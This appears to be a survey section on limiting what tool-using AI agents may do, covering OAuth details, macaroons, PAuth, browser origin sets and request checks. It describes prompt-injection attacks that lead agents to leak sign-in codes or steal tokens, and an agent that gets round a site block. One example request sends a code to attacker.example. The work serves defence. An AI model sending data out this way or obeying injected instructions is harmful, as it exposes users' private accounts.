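*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* lists what a scope such as files.read leaves out: the purpose of the task, the relevant documents, the permitted recipients, the number of calls, and an expiry tied to the end of the task. Adding more scopes would help only with a few common cases. A bank could define a scope for transfers of up to $500, but it couldn't define one for every combination of amount and recipient. A permission for a single task has to include values such as the amount and recipient, or the service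 has to work them out from the task.

### Rich Authorization Requests

Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell (2023), in *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, added a field for such values to OAuth. Their standard, RFC 9396, lets an application describe the access it wants in a field called authorization_details. For Alice's transfer, the request might contain:

```
"authorization_details": [{
  "type": "payment_initiation",
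  "actions": ["initiate"],
  "instructedAmount": { "currency": "USD", "amount": "100.00" },
  "creditorName": "Bob",
  "creditorAccount": { "number": "4471902" }
}]
```

Alice can now approve a $100 transfer to Bob on the consent screen, rather than transfers in general. If she does, the authorization server puts the details in the token or supplies them when the bank looks the token up. The bank compares each transfer with those details and refuses it if the amount or recipient is different. The bank also has to decide whether the approval covers one payment or several, because the details in this example don't specify that.

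Alice can also fill in part of the request herself. An application might ask to read account information without naming an account. She then chooses one on the consent screen, and the authorization server adds the account number to the details.

A mail service could support the invoice task in the same way, by allowing the agent to search, read and draft messages, with the accountant's address as the only correspondent. But the standard defines only the general format and a few common fields. Each service must define its own types, display them clearly on the consent screen and enforce them. An authorization server must reject any type or field it doesn't recognise, so an application can't add a sender limit that the mail service hasn't implemented.

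The format also makes it easy to request too much by accident. An entry that lists the actions "read" and "write" and the data types "contacts" and "photos" allows all four combinations. An application that only needs to read contacts and write photos must therefore use two entries. There is no standard way to tell whether one request covers more access than another, because each service decides what its fields mean.

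The larger difficulty is that some values aren't known when the task starts. If Alice asks an agent to pay a quarter of her credit card balance, the application can't fill in the amount until the agent has looked up the balance. The application could request permission to pay up to $500, but then a misled agent could pay $499 when the right amount was $100. It could also wait until it knows the amount and ask Alice again. IETF's *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling* (2026), a draft, would help with this second approach by letting a service that refuses a call return the exact details the application should request. Alice might still face a new consent screen each time.

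*Beyond OAuth* argues that Rich Authorization Requests therefore amount to approving every call. This is a fair criticism for longer tasks in which each step depends on the last. But if all of a task's values are known at the start, one request can contain several entries, and Alice can approve them together.

Asking for approval more often can also backfire. Bucci, Caballero and colleagues warn in *Delegated Authority Problem Space Report* that a user may grant the agent broad permissions just to stop the interruptions. Silverlock's *The Agent Access Model*, a proposal from Cloudflare, would reserve approvals for setting a task's limits and for a few high-risk actions.

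### Macaroons

*AIP* (2026), a proposal for agent identity, points out that only the authorization server can narrow an ordinary OAuth token. If Alice's application holds a token for her whole mailbox, it can't restrict that token to messages from one sender before giving it to an agent. In *Macaroons* (2014), Birgisson, Politz and colleagues designed a credential that its holder can narrow without contacting the service that issued it.

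A macaroon contains an identifier, a list of restrictions called caveats, and a signature. The signature comes from HMAC, a function that turns a secret key and a message into a short value. Nobody can feasibly work out the key from that value.

Suppose the mail service gives Alice's application a macaroon for her whole mailbox. The service keeps a secret key, K, and uses it to compute the first signature, s0. The application then adds three caveats for the invoice task. Each time, the current signature becomes the key for the next one:

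```
s0 = HMAC(K,  "alice-mailbox-82")
s1 = HMAC(s0, "operation is search, read or draft")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "correspondent is accounts@ledger.example")
s3 = HMAC(s2, "time is before 10:10 UTC on 5 December 2026")
```

The application gives the agent the identifier, the three caveats and s3. It keeps s0, s1 and s2 to itself.

To remove the time limit, the agent would need to present the first two caveats with s2, which it can't recover from s3. It can't remove the correspondent caveat either, because it would need a signature computed from s1 and the time limit, and it doesn't have s1.

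The agent can add a fourth caveat because s3 is the key for the next step. This is useful for passing a smaller part of the job to another agent. It can't gain access by adding a caveat, though. Adding "operation is send" would produce a macaroon that permits nothing, since a request must satisfy every caveat and sending isn't one of the original three operations.

This works only if the agent cannot access the earlier signatures. If the application leaves the original macaroon in a file the agent can read, the agent can use it and avoid the caveats.

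#### What the mail service must check

When the agent makes a request, the mail service recomputes the chain from K and compares the result with s3. A match shows that nobody has removed or changed a caveat. The service must then check that the request satisfies every caveat.

| Caveat | Check by the mail service |
|---|---|
| Operation | The request is a search, a read or a draft. |
| Correspondent | The accountant sent the message the agent wants to read. Search results contain only the accountant's messages. A draft has no other recipient. |
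| Time | The service's own clock shows a time before 10:10. |

To check the correspondent, the service has to define "correspondent" for each operation and authenticate the sender, because a stranger can type the accountant's address into the "From" line of an email. A macaroon can carry this limit securely, but a service like Gmail would still need code to enforce it. Under the procedure in *Macaroons*, the service refuses a request if it can't confirm that a caveat holds.

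The service must also check that Alice still has the access herself and hasn't revoked the macaroon. If the service later adds an operation, existing macaroons may permit it unintentionally. Birgisson and colleagues give the example of a storage service that adds a delete operation after issuing macaroons that don't restrict operations. Alice's list of three permitted operations would exclude any new operation, whereas a caveat that only prohibited sending would allow it.

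Caveats in the original macaroon design can set time limits and restrict a request's arguments, so *AIP* is partly wrong to describe them as too simple for time limits, budgets or conditions on a tool's parameters. Budgets are harder because the service must keep a running total of what the agent has spent, which the macaroon can't store.

#### Conditions that another service confirms

A caveat can also require proof from another service. Alice's application could add the condition that she is still signed in with her identity provider. The agent would then have to get a short-lived proof from the provider and present it with its requests. When Alice signed out, the provider would stop issuing proofs, and the agent would lose access when its last proof expired. The proof is also a macaroon, and the mail service can check it without contacting the provider.

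Creating a macaroon takes so little computation that each task can have its own. In the researchers' Python prototype, adding a caveat took about 55 microseconds and verifying a macaroon took about 96. The main technical drawback is that only the service with the secret key can verify a macaroon. Anyone who holds a macaroon can also use it unless a caveat prevents this, although a thief who copies the agent's version gets only the narrowed access.

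Caveats can't reliably stop an agent from sharing its access. Bucci and colleagues point out that someone forbidden to pass on a permission can simply carry out requests for another party. The service then can't tell who originally made the request.

In a slide deck, Madden (2024) explains how an OAuth token can be a macaroon, with the scope, audience and expiry time as caveats. If the holder adds an earlier expiry time, the authorization server reports that time to any service that looks up the token. Madden also gives the lack of a standard as a reason not to use macaroons. Birgisson and colleagues suggested using macaroons as session cookies, so that a browser could make a cookie valid for only a few seconds before sending it.

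### Limits that tighten during a task

Some permissions are reasonably safe separately but dangerous together. An agent that can read private records and also write to strangers can leak the records. *Bounded Agents* (2026) therefore defines a permission with four parts: the resources R, the types of action A, the classes of data D, and the pairs of actions X that the agent may not combine. When one agent delegates to another, their permissions combine as follows:

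```
R = R1 ∩ R2
A = A1 ∩ A2
D = D1 ∩ D2
X = X1 ∪ X2
```

The second agent gets only the access that both permissions allow, and every prohibited pair from either permission still applies. To enforce the prohibited pairs, the system must keep a record of what the agents have already done. Enforcement also depends on how finely the system divides actions into types. If posting to a private channel and emailing a stranger count as the same type, a rule meant to stop only the email will also block the post.

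Silverlock proposes removing permissions as soon as an agent touches sensitive data. In one example, a finance agent collects a report from a payment processor, compares it with two ledgers and posts a summary to a company channel. At first, the agent can also contact the processor's support desk. When the report arrives, the system cuts off access to the processor and the support desk before showing the report to the model. If a ledger contains instructions to attach the account history to a support case, the agent can no longer do so, even though the original task allowed support requests.

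The same example shows one way to protect a value that the agent produces during a task. Trusted software checks the summary, stores it and gives the agent an identifier. The posting operation accepts only that identifier, so the agent can't substitute other text after the check. The operation always posts to the same channel, and the summary has a fixed format with no free-text field.

This suits a job that runs every night, because a company can define its limits once and refine them using the logs. It is less useful for Alice's invoice, a one-off task that nobody planned for. Silverlock presents a design but no test results, and acknowledges that broad rules will block some harmless work.

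### PAuth

*Beyond OAuth*, a paper by researchers from the University of Washington, Ohio State University and Microsoft Research, describes PAuth (Precise Task-Scoped Implicit Authorization), which handles a one-off task by sending it to the services involved. Each service works out from the user's words which calls to expect, so the user approves the task once instead of approving each permission.

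Their main example is the request "pay a quarter of my Citi balance using my Chase account". It would work as follows:

1. The user reviews and signs the text of the task, and the agent's software sends it to Citi and Chase. The signature prevents the agent from changing the text.
2. A language model at each bank translates the task into a short program in a restricted form of Python. The bank never runs this program. Ordinary software extracts from it the parts that determine the calls to that bank.
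3. Chase now expects a transfer from the user's Chase account to the user's Citi account, for the Citi balance divided by four.
4. The agent asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns $400 with a label stating where the number came from, and signs both.
5. The agent asks Chase to transfer $100 and includes Citi's signed value.
6. Chase verifies Citi's signature, divides 400 by 4, and checks the amount and recipient. They match, so it makes the transfer.

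If the agent asked to pay $101, or to pay $100 to another recipient, Chase would stop and ask the user about that specific payment. The agent couldn't avoid this by inventing a balance of $404, because it can't produce Citi's signature. If the task had also required the balance to exceed $1,000, Chase would check that too and wouldn't make this payment without asking.

Hossen's check in the consent experiment also compared requests with the task, but it relied on a list of permitted approvals. PAuth derives the expected calls from the task, including values that come from another service. It uses the language model once, before the agent starts. After that, it compares requests with the expected calls using fixed rules, so text on a malicious page can't influence the comparison.

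#### The test results

The researchers tested PAuth on 100 tasks involving simulated banking, messaging, travel, office and shopping services. They based most of these on AgentDojo, a benchmark for agent security. They also wrote 634 adversarial calls that changed a value such as the amount or recipient, used a tool the task didn't need, or tried to skip a condition.

| Wording of the tasks | Tasks completed without asking the user | Adversarial calls blocked |
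|---|---|---|
| Original | 71 of 100 | 634 of 634 |
| Rewritten to supply missing details | 100 of 100 | 634 of 634 |

In these results, "blocked" means that the service asked the user for permission, and the call would go through if the user approved. The prompt is much better than an ordinary consent screen because it gives the actual amount and recipient, and it appears only when a call doesn't match the task. But the results don't show that users would have refused the 634 blocked calls.

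PAuth avoided many routine prompts. Of the 100 tasks, 44 needed at least three calls and 26 needed at least five. With the rewritten wording, users wouldn't have had to approve any of these calls individually. The language model cost between $0.002 and $0.038 per task on average, depending on the model and the group of tasks, and each service involved has to pay for its own translation.

The adversarial calls came from a fixed set, and none of the three kinds repeated a correct payment. The published matching procedure compares a call with the expected one but has no step that marks the expected call as used, so it may let an agent make a correct $100 payment twice. A bank would need its own protection against that.

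#### How realistic the assumptions are

PAuth requires an unambiguous task, and 29 of the original 100 tasks were ambiguous. Some told the agent to follow instructions in a file, while others left out a time or an amount. The researchers had to supply the missing details to reach the perfect score. People often delegate tasks to avoid looking up these details.

A task that sounds clear can still be ambiguous. In one test, the user asked the agent to refund $10 that a friend had just sent. The bank's rule searched recent transactions for an incoming $10 payment and allowed a refund to its sender. If two people had each sent $10, the rule could select the wrong sender, even though every value would have a genuine signature.

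PAuth is also limited when the agent has to write text, as in Alice's invoice task, because no service can predict the reply's exact words. PAuth treats anything that a language model will compose as a value that nothing can match, so the mail service would have to ask Alice about the draft. She intended to read it anyway, but if the agent wrote 30 replies, the service would have to ask her 30 times. PAuth works best for payments, bookings and other calls whose values come from a calculation or a lookup.

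The user must also review each task carefully before signing it, especially when the agent has rewritten it. If the user wants a balance sent to the third address in a contacts file, the agent can look up the address, put it in the text and highlight it for approval. An agent misled by the file could insert an attacker's address instead, and PAuth would then authorize that message. Reviewing one task carefully is easier than approving five calls, but people can skim a task as easily as a consent screen.

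Every participating service needs a language model that can translate the task correctly. GPT-4.1 did this for all 100 tasks in the main test, and three other models made no errors on smaller sets. The researchers argue that most translation errors would only cause extra prompts, since PAuth refuses any unexpected call. That is true of a wrong amount or recipient, but a model that left out a condition could allow a payment the user wanted to prevent. No such error occurred in the tests, though the tasks were short and mostly explicit.

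The last drawback is reduced privacy. Chase receives the full text of the task and Citi's signed balance, whereas an ordinary transfer would reveal only the amount. The prototype sends the text to every connected service, even those not involved in the task. If Alice asked an agent to pay a divorce lawyer and order groceries, the grocer would learn about the lawyer. The researchers regard disclosure as unavoidable, because a service can't check whether an agent is following a task without seeing the task. Splitting the request into separate tasks would help when the parts are unrelated.

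Services could adopt PAuth one at a time. For a website that hasn't adopted it, a company could run a trusted intermediary that holds the OAuth token and checks each call against the task before forwarding it. Security would then depend on the intermediary, because the website would still accept any call the token allowed.

### Matching tasks to scopes automatically

A less ambitious approach keeps existing scopes and uses a language model to choose among them. *Delegated Authorization for Agents Constrained to Semantic Task-to-Scope Matching* (El Helou, Troiani and colleagues, 2025) proposes a trusted intermediary that records the user's task before passing it to the agent. When the agent requests scopes, the intermediary forwards the request and the original task to the authorization server. A model on the server judges whether each scope fits the task, and the server issues a token with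 only the approved ones. Because the server gets the task from the intermediary, the agent can't justify a larger request by misreporting what the user wanted.

The researchers tested this with synthetic tasks based on 12 public servers that use the Model Context Protocol. They treated each tool on a server as a separate permission. For every task, they presented GPT-4o with both the tools it needed and some it didn't. The unneeded tools mostly came from the same server as the needed ones, so they were often related to the task.

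| Tools needed for the task | Decisions that were correct | Needed tools that the model approved | Approved tools that the task needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| One | 96% | 99% | 93% |
| Two | 86% | 82% | 89% |
| Three | 72% | 57% | 81% |

When a task needed three tools, the main problem was wrongful refusal. A task usually fails if the agent lacks even one tool it needs. If the model approves each needed tool 57% of the time and its decisions are independent, it will approve all three only about 19% of the time, so it will wrongly refuse at least one in about 81% of tasks. El Helou and colleagues found a similar rate of wrongful refusal, 78%, when they looked at whole tasks.

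The model did better on an outside dataset whose tasks listed their steps more explicitly, getting 82% of decisions right for three tools. This suggests that vague requests caused much of the difficulty. GPT-4o is well behind the models of late 2026, so these figures probably understate what the method can do now. But the researchers picked the incorrect tools at random, while an attacker would choose ones that looked plausible.

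They also tested a simpler matcher that had a model describe the ideal tool and then compared this description with the real tools. It almost never approved a wrong tool, but when a task needed one tool, it approved the right one only 55% of the time.

This approach can only choose among the permissions a service already offers, and better models wouldn't change that. If the task is to pay Bob $100, even a perfect matcher would give the agent the transfer scope, and the agent could still pay someone else. The matcher would also have to choose between grants in the cases where, as Xu found, no single grant is the smallest. One remedy is to add narrower limits after choosing the scopes. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026), a survey, describes a system called CAPMAS that does this with macaroons.

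### A payment token with built-in limits

Payment companies already issue credentials that are limited in some of these ways. In September 2025, Stripe introduced the Shared Payment Token, which lets an AI agent pay a seller without revealing the customer's card number. The token names one seller, a maximum amount and an expiry time. The seller uses it to charge the customer through Stripe, which enforces the limits.

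If Alice asks an agent to buy running shoes for up to $100, the token could allow one shop to charge up to $100 within the next hour. An attacker who persuaded the agent to send the token to another shop would gain nothing. The agent could still buy the wrong shoes, or pay $100 for a pair that should have cost $60, because the token restricts only the shop, the amount and the time.

The payment token is practical partly because almost every purchase has the same few important values (seller, amount and time), and one company can check all three for many shops. Mail has no equally simple set of limits that would suit most tasks.

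### Resources that an agent creates

A payment can stay within its limits and still give an agent more power than the user intended. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* describes an agent that is allowed to spend $20 on a cloud computer with read-only access. The price, order and receipt are all correct, but the computer comes with an administrator's credential and can affect outside systems. If the agent can use that credential immediately, the original limits no longer restrict it.

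The paper proposes that software outside the agent first hold any new resource in quarantine. The software checks with the provider what the resource can do, then separately decides whether the agent may use it. The agent never receives the raw credential and has to make its requests through the software. This also covers cases that a spending limit would miss, such as an agent opening four free accounts when it was supposed to have one, or getting a refund for a service but keeping the credential.

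Cloud providers already separate some of these decisions. Amazon's cloud service, for example, requires one permission to start a computer and another to give it a particular role. In the paper's own tests, the proposed rules accepted all 20 harmless sequences of events and rejected all 40 unsafe ones, but the researchers had defined them in advance. The method also needs reliable information from the provider. If that information is missing, the resource stays in quarantine and the agent may be unable to finish its task.

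## Limits the browser can place on a signed-in agent

The browser stores Alice's cookies, loads the pages and sends the requests, so it can withhold a session, keep an agent off a site or block an operation without help from the website. These limits apply only while the agent uses that browser.

### Separate profiles and signed-out browsing

An agent doesn't need a signed-in session to compare flight prices or summarise a public page. Browsers can keep several profiles, each with its own cookies, and a new profile starts signed out of every site. The Comet agent that searched for a login code would have found Gmail's sign-in page instead of the user's mail if it had been running in such a profile.

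For the invoice task, Alice could create a profile for the agent and sign in only to her webmail there. The agent would have no session at her bank, and she could end its webmail session without ending her own. She should keep her saved passwords out of the profile, since the agent might otherwise use them to sign in elsewhere. But the profile wouldn't stop the agent from performing any of the eight operations in the mailbox.

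Sood (2026) reports in *Gemini Spark now works with Chrome* that Google's Spark agent can, with the user's permission, use their saved credentials and the accounts they are already signed in to. For example, it might write to landlords about apartments the user has bookmarked. An agent in an empty browser profile would have neither the bookmarks nor the accounts.

### Agent Origin Sets

Chrome lets the agent use the signed-in browser but restricts which sites it can use for each task. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) calls this design Agent Origin Sets. When the agent's planning model proposes a site, a gating function decides whether that site's origin is relevant to the task. The gating function doesn't see web content, so text on a malicious page can't reach it directly.

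The design sorts the approved origins into two sets:

- **Read-only origins.** The agent can read their content but can't act on them.
- **Read-writable origins.** The agent can also click and type.

Suppose a user asks the agent to collect ingredients from a recipe site and put them in a cart at a grocery shop. The recipe site could be read-only and the shop's site read-writable, while the user's bank site would be neither. If the recipe page contains an advertisement in a frame from an unrelated origin, Chrome doesn't show it to the model. Hidden instructions in the recipe itself could still mislead the agent, but it couldn't open the bank's site unless the gating function approved that origin.

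Chrome also checks whether a new origin is relevant to the task when the agent tries to go there or a page redirects it there. The check uses a variant of the User Alignment Critic, a second model that receives only a description of each proposed action and vetoes those that don't serve the user's goal.

The browser enforces the sets, but their contents depend on a judgment about relevance, which is harder to make when the task is vague. The first version tracked only the read-writable set. In early 2026, Roesner and Kohlbrenner found that Chrome's agent still had the access a cross-site attack would need.

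Some steps also require the user's confirmation:

| Step | How Chrome recognises it |
|---|---|
| Opening certain sensitive sites, such as banking or medical sites | A fixed list of sites |
| Signing in with Google Password Manager | The agent has to ask Chrome for the sign-in, and the model has no direct access to the password |
| Buying, paying, sending a message or taking another consequential action | A mixture of fixed rules and models |

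The last row is the least certain. Parker writes that the agent "will try to pause" before these actions and that Google is still improving the classifiers for unclear cases.

### Chrome and Claude in late 2026

Google launched Chrome's agent, called auto browse, in January 2026, as reported in Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026). By mid-October it was available to paying subscribers in India on desktop and Android, according to Kanchwala, in *Gemini Can Now Browse For You, But Should You Let It?*

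*Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) confirms that in August Chrome still limited the agent to origins relevant to the task. The agent stops for approval before it finalises a contract, makes a payment or sends a mass email. It keeps a log of its steps, and Chrome's history labels the background pages it visited. Mass email is only one of Berschadski's examples, so the approval rule may also cover single messages. If it doesn't, it wouldn't protect Alice, because a single message can leak a sign-in code.

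Anthropic's Claude in Chrome relies more on the user to choose which sites it can access. According to Anthropic, users can mark a site as always allowed, review the approved sites and revoke any of them. A company's administrators can limit Claude to a list of sites or block particular ones, regardless of what the user has allowed. Some actions need explicit permission in every mode.

Both products define access mainly by site. Alice's agent has to type a search and write a draft, so she must let it act on her webmail site. The same permission also covers sending, deleting and forwarding. Confirmations reduce the risk only if the software recognises what a click will do and Alice reads the prompt.

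A newer proposal from Chromium engineers has the same difficulty. Europa Press' *Google propone un sistema de permisos en Chrome para restringir las acciones* (2026) describes planned changes to WebDriver BiDi, a protocol that lets outside software control a browser. Developers designed it for automated testing, so they assumed that software could be trusted completely. Under the proposal, an agent would start with only default permissions and ask for more. A list would set the origins it could visit, the commands it could send and the browser events it could receive, for the whole browser or for certain tabs. The user could see which tabs an agent was operating, and could pause or stop the agent.

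The proposed "restricted session" limits the agent's connection to the browser, not the user's session at the website. If the list of allowed actions includes clicking on a page, the browser can't distinguish an ordinary button from one that deletes information. The proposal is at an early stage, and its developers want it to work across different browsers.

### Checking requests instead of clicks

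The effect of a click depends on the page and the size of the window, so clicking the same position on the screen might open a message or delete it. Blocking one kind of action also doesn't reliably stop an agent. In *CELLMATE*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) tried to keep an agent off Hacker News by forbidding it to go there directly, but it searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

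The CELLMATE system checks the request that a click produces. To delete a message or add a password, the browser normally has to send an HTTP request to the website, and the request's method and address usually identify the operation. On the code-hosting service GitLab, for example, a POST request to /-/user_settings/ssh_keys adds an SSH key that can give its owner access to the user's code. The request is the same whether the agent clicked a button, pressed a key or followed a misleading link.

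The browser still needs to know what each request means. Meng and colleagues propose that websites publish an "agent sitemap", a map from requests to named operations. Alice's webmail might publish a map like this one:

| Request | Operation | Decision for the invoice task |
|---|---|---|
| GET /search* | Search | Allow |
| GET /messages/* | Read | Allow |
| POST /drafts | Draft | Allow |
| POST /messages/send | Send | Block |
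| POST /settings/forwarding | Set forwarding | Block |

An entry can also match a request's content, which helps if a site uses one address for several operations. The website or another trusted party then writes policies that allow, deny or conditionally allow operations. In an Amazon example, the agent may place an order only if it totals $50 or less. CELLMATE reads the total from the checkout page and compares it with the limit when the browser sends the order. The agent could get around this limit by placing two $49 orders, so CELLMATE can also count requests and allow only one.

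At the start of a task, a language model identifies the websites named in the task, then selects the smallest set of policies that covers the work on each site. Its input includes the user's request and the policy descriptions but no web pages, so a malicious page can't influence the selection. The user confirms or changes the selection, which then stays fixed until the user updates it.

#### How well models chose the policies

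Meng and colleagues tested GPT-5.1, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Opus 4.5 on 209 tasks. For some policies, the model had to extract a value, such as a maximum price, from the task.

| Type of website | Correct set of policies | Correct policies and values, where a task needed values |
|---|---|---|
| Retail | 96.6% to 99.3% of 149 tasks | 81.3% to 96.9% of 32 tasks |
| Travel | 94.4% to 100% of 36 tasks | 100% of 5 tasks |
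| Code hosting | 95.8% to 100% of 24 tasks | No such tasks |

These results are much better than those El Helou and colleagues got for matching tasks to scopes. The models were different, and Meng and colleagues had also rewritten vague tasks to include details such as a product or spending limit. Their system refuses access if the user doesn't name a website, as in "purchase a coffee maker" instead of "purchase a coffee maker on Amazon."

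The models made several kinds of errors. One confused a wishlist with a shopping cart because the task mentioned a price limit. Another response let the agent create a list but not rename it, although the task required both. A missing policy stops the task, while an extra one lets a misled agent take actions the task doesn't need. The user can correct either error before the task starts, but may not notice an extra policy.

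Meng and colleagues require a site's policies to form a partial order (a ranking that may leave some pairs unranked) based on the actions each allows. They say this makes the least-privileged choice clear, but a task could still have no single least-privileged choice, as Xu found with Microsoft's and Google's scopes. To avoid this, a site would need to divide its policies so that every common task had one.

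#### Blocking a compromised agent

The security test used WASP, a benchmark of prompt injection attacks on browser agents. In a replication by Meng and colleagues, WASP's original attacks succeeded from start to finish less than 17% of the time against OpenAI's o1 and less than 7% of the time against the other models. A defence could therefore look effective simply because the agent ignored the attack.

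The researchers instead assumed that the attacker had full control of the agent. They wrote 12 scripts, one for each of the benchmark's attack goals on GitLab, such as stealing access tokens, deleting a project or adding the attacker as a collaborator. The user's tasks were to comment on an issue (a discussion page for a problem) and to upvote one. CELLMATE selected permission to read and write issues, then blocked all 12 scripts.

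This is good evidence that the request check works even if the model is completely compromised. But every attack needed an operation the policy didn't allow. CELLMATE doesn't check the content of comments, so an agent with permission to comment could still post a harmful comment or reveal information in one.

CELLMATE added little delay. A series of 11 page navigations took 13.93 seconds without it, 14.94 seconds with a map of 100 entries and 16.02 seconds with 300 entries, an increase of 7.25% to 15%. That adds roughly a tenth to a fifth of a second per navigation, which a user would hardly notice while waiting for the agent's model.

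CELLMATE doesn't cover WebSockets, which let a page and a server exchange messages over a continuous connection. Many sites use them for live updates, often in private formats that a general browser tool can't interpret. If Alice's webmail sent email over a WebSocket, a map of HTTP requests wouldn't stop the agent from sending it.

### Hiding parts of a page

Sharma and Grossman's AC4A system hides any part of a page that the agent has no permission to use. Each permission combines a resource in the user's data, such as one month of a calendar, with an action. A calendar application arranges its resources by year, month and day, so permission for June covers every day in June.

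When the agent tries to use a resource, AC4A works out which permissions would be sufficient and subtracts those the user has granted. It allows access only if nothing remains:

```
remaining = needed - granted
allow if remaining is empty for every action
```

In the table below, the user has granted permission to read their calendar for June 2026. The first three rows follow Sharma and Grossman's demonstration in Outlook Calendar, and the last shows a request that spans two months.

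| The agent tries to | Permission still missing | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Read June 2026 | None | Allowed |
| Read July 2026 | Read July 2026 | Blocked |
| Create an event on 29 June 2026 | Create on 29 June 2026 | Blocked |
| Read 28 June to 3 July 2026 | Read 1 to 3 July 2026 | Blocked |

In AC4A, a configuration file connects each part of a web page to a resource and an action. For Outlook, AC4A reads the month and year from the label above the calendar. If the agent moves from June to July, the label changes, and AC4A checks the agent's permissions again and covers the calendar with a dark box with a cross before the agent sees it. AC4A also keeps the button for adding an event covered because the agent has no permission to create one.

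This could fit Alice's invoice task more closely than a list of operations alone. If the configuration recognised senders, the browser could hide every message except the accountant's. CELLMATE, by contrast, controls access to a whole response, so a request for the inbox would normally return everyone's messages.

CELLMATE is better than AC4A at blocking operations. Covering a Delete button might not stop the agent from using a keyboard shortcut, but CELLMATE would check the resulting request. CELLMATE can also check a payment against a limit. AC4A doesn't support conditions on values, so its developers would have to model "checkout under $200" as a separate resource.

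AC4A's permissions also last until the user removes them. An agent with permission to change one event could later delete another on the same day. Sharma and Grossman tested the system through demonstrations, including a flight booking on Expedia, and didn't measure how often it blocks legitimate work or misses something on a page.

### Writing and maintaining the maps

Both systems depend on someone describing each website correctly. Meng and colleagues expect the website's own developers to do this, because those developers know what each request does. For GitLab, the researchers mapped 51 operations by hand using the site's routing code, which connects addresses to operations. They compare the work to writing API documentation, which many developers already do.

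Outsiders can also write AC4A's configuration files. Sharma and Grossman made one for Outlook without Microsoft's help. Such files would let users protect themselves on sites whose owners show no interest in agents, but a file can stop working when the site's pages change. Sharma and Grossman consider maintenance the system's most important practical limitation.

A change to the site could make the restrictions too strict or too loose. If Alice's webmail moved its draft operation to a new address, a policy tied to the old address might stop the agent from saving her reply. An outdated sitemap might also fail to restrict a new button for sharing the mailbox. AC4A leaves page elements visible when no rule matches them, and Meng and colleagues say an incomplete or incorrect sitemap leaves the user with the ordinary level of protection.

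They argue that this introduces no new security risk. That is reasonable if the user would have delegated the same task anyway, but a user who trusts the restriction may delegate more sensitive work. Blocking all unlisted requests would be safer, but it would also block harmless ones until someone added them to the map.

A website's developers could attach permanent identifiers to the checkout total or the Save button, so that a redesign wouldn't break browser rules that refer to them. They would still have to label new features and test the restrictions after each change.

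### When the agent leaves the controlled browser

CELLMATE assumes that the agent can act only within web pages and cannot change browser settings, use developer tools or read local files. The prototype is a Chrome extension, so it also assumes that no other extension interferes with its requests. Companies can enforce some of these conditions through Chrome's administrative settings, and a browser maker could build the check into the browser.

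An agent with broader access to the computer could avoid these limits. It might open another browser or copy Alice's cookies into a program that sends requests directly. The webmail server would accept the cookies and carry out the operation, since the restrictions exist only in the first browser. Device Bound Session Credentials would make copied cookies expire quickly, but wouldn't stop the agent from opening Chrome without the extension.

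If an agent runs in a provider's remote browser, the limits have to be in that browser, because an extension on Alice's computer doesn't affect it. AC4A can also apply the same permissions to API calls, but only if those calls pass through its checks.

### Disclosure through read-only access

An agent doesn't need permission to send mail in order to leak it. Suppose Alice's agent may read her mailbox and open other web pages, but can't click or type on any site. A stranger's email persuades it to find a sign-in code and open an address that contains the code:

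```
GET /page?code=482913 HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example
```

The attacker's server records the address and now has the code. The request fetched a page and changed nothing in Alice's account, so a rule that blocked only changes would allow it.

Meng and colleagues cite the developer Simon Willison, who identifies three conditions for this kind of attack: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. Alice's mailbox supplies the first two. The browser can most easily restrict the third by limiting where requests may go.

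In Parker's design, Agent Origin Sets let data from approved origins pass only to writable origins. Chrome checks a new origin for relevance before the agent goes there. It also limits addresses written by the model to known public ones, so an address containing Alice's private code is unlikely to be allowed.

Restricting addresses to known pages isn't enough by itself to prevent leaks. An attacker could publish ten pages, one for each digit, and have the agent reveal a six-digit code by opening the matching pages in order. No single address would contain the code. The relevance check should stop this by keeping the agent off the attacker's origin, provided it judges that origin correctly.

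CELLMATE blocks requests to unrelated sites by default, which would also stop the request to attacker.example. A policy can list extra domains that a page needs for images or other content, but each added domain is another place data could be sent. CELLMATE doesn't track whether private information influenced a permitted request.

Limiting which sites the agent can reach doesn't stop it from leaking data within an approved site, as happened through Instagram's chat. To prevent that, the browser needs to limit both what the agent can read and how it can communicate on the site. Hiding most of the mailbox protects the hidden messages on every site, because the model can't disclose text it never received.

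Other tools inspect or track the data itself. According to Berschadski, Chrome's paid enterprise version can check data that agents handle and block some transfers of sensitive material to public language models. Research systems such as CaMeL and FIDES track where information came from and restrict its later use. FIDES, for example, attaches confidentiality labels to data, as Sharma and Grossman explain. Meng and colleagues point out that these systems are hard to apply to an agent that only clicks and types, because they depend on operations with clear meanings, such as "send email".

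## Restricted sessions enforced by the website

A website's server can limit an agent regardless of which browser or program it uses, because every operation on Alice's mail passes through that server. The server also runs the code for each operation, so nobody has to infer a request's effect from outside the server. To restrict the agent, the server needs a session record that distinguishes the agent from Alice and lists what the agent may do.

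### How mail.example could issue a restricted session

For the invoice task, the process might run as follows:

1. Alice opens a delegation page in her account. She selects search, read and draft, enters the accountant's address, and sets a limit of ten minutes.
2. The server sends these limits to her phone, where she approves them with her fingerprint.
3. The server creates a new session record for the agent, with its own random identifier.
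4. The server issues a link that works once. The agent opens it in a separate browser profile and receives a cookie containing the new identifier.
5. The server checks each of the agent's requests against the record, then carries out the operation or refuses it.
6. When the server refuses an operation, it notifies Alice directly.
7. Alice can end the agent's session from her account page at any time. The server deletes that one record, and her own session continues.

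The record might contain this:

```
8f1c60b2d7e94a35
  user:           alice
  agent:          invoice-7
  operations:     search, read, draft
  correspondent:  accounts@ledger.example
  expires:        10:10 UTC, 5 December 2026
```

Alice has to approve the limits with something the agent doesn't hold, because an agent in her browser could click an ordinary Approve button. She can do this on her phone, where a screen the agent doesn't control shows her the limits the server is about to store. A code sent to her mailbox doesn't help if the agent can read her mail. A security key would prove that she was present but not that she had read the limits, so she might touch it without noticing that a misled agent had filled in the delegation page with broader permissions.

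The separate profile in step 4 is just as important. Alice's usual profile contains the cookie for her full session, so an agent working there could use that session instead of the restricted one.

For each request, the server applies the intersection rule from OAuth, extended to cover individual messages:

```
allow if  the session is still valid
     and  Alice may perform this operation on this message
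     and  the record lists the operation
     and  the message falls within the record's limits
```

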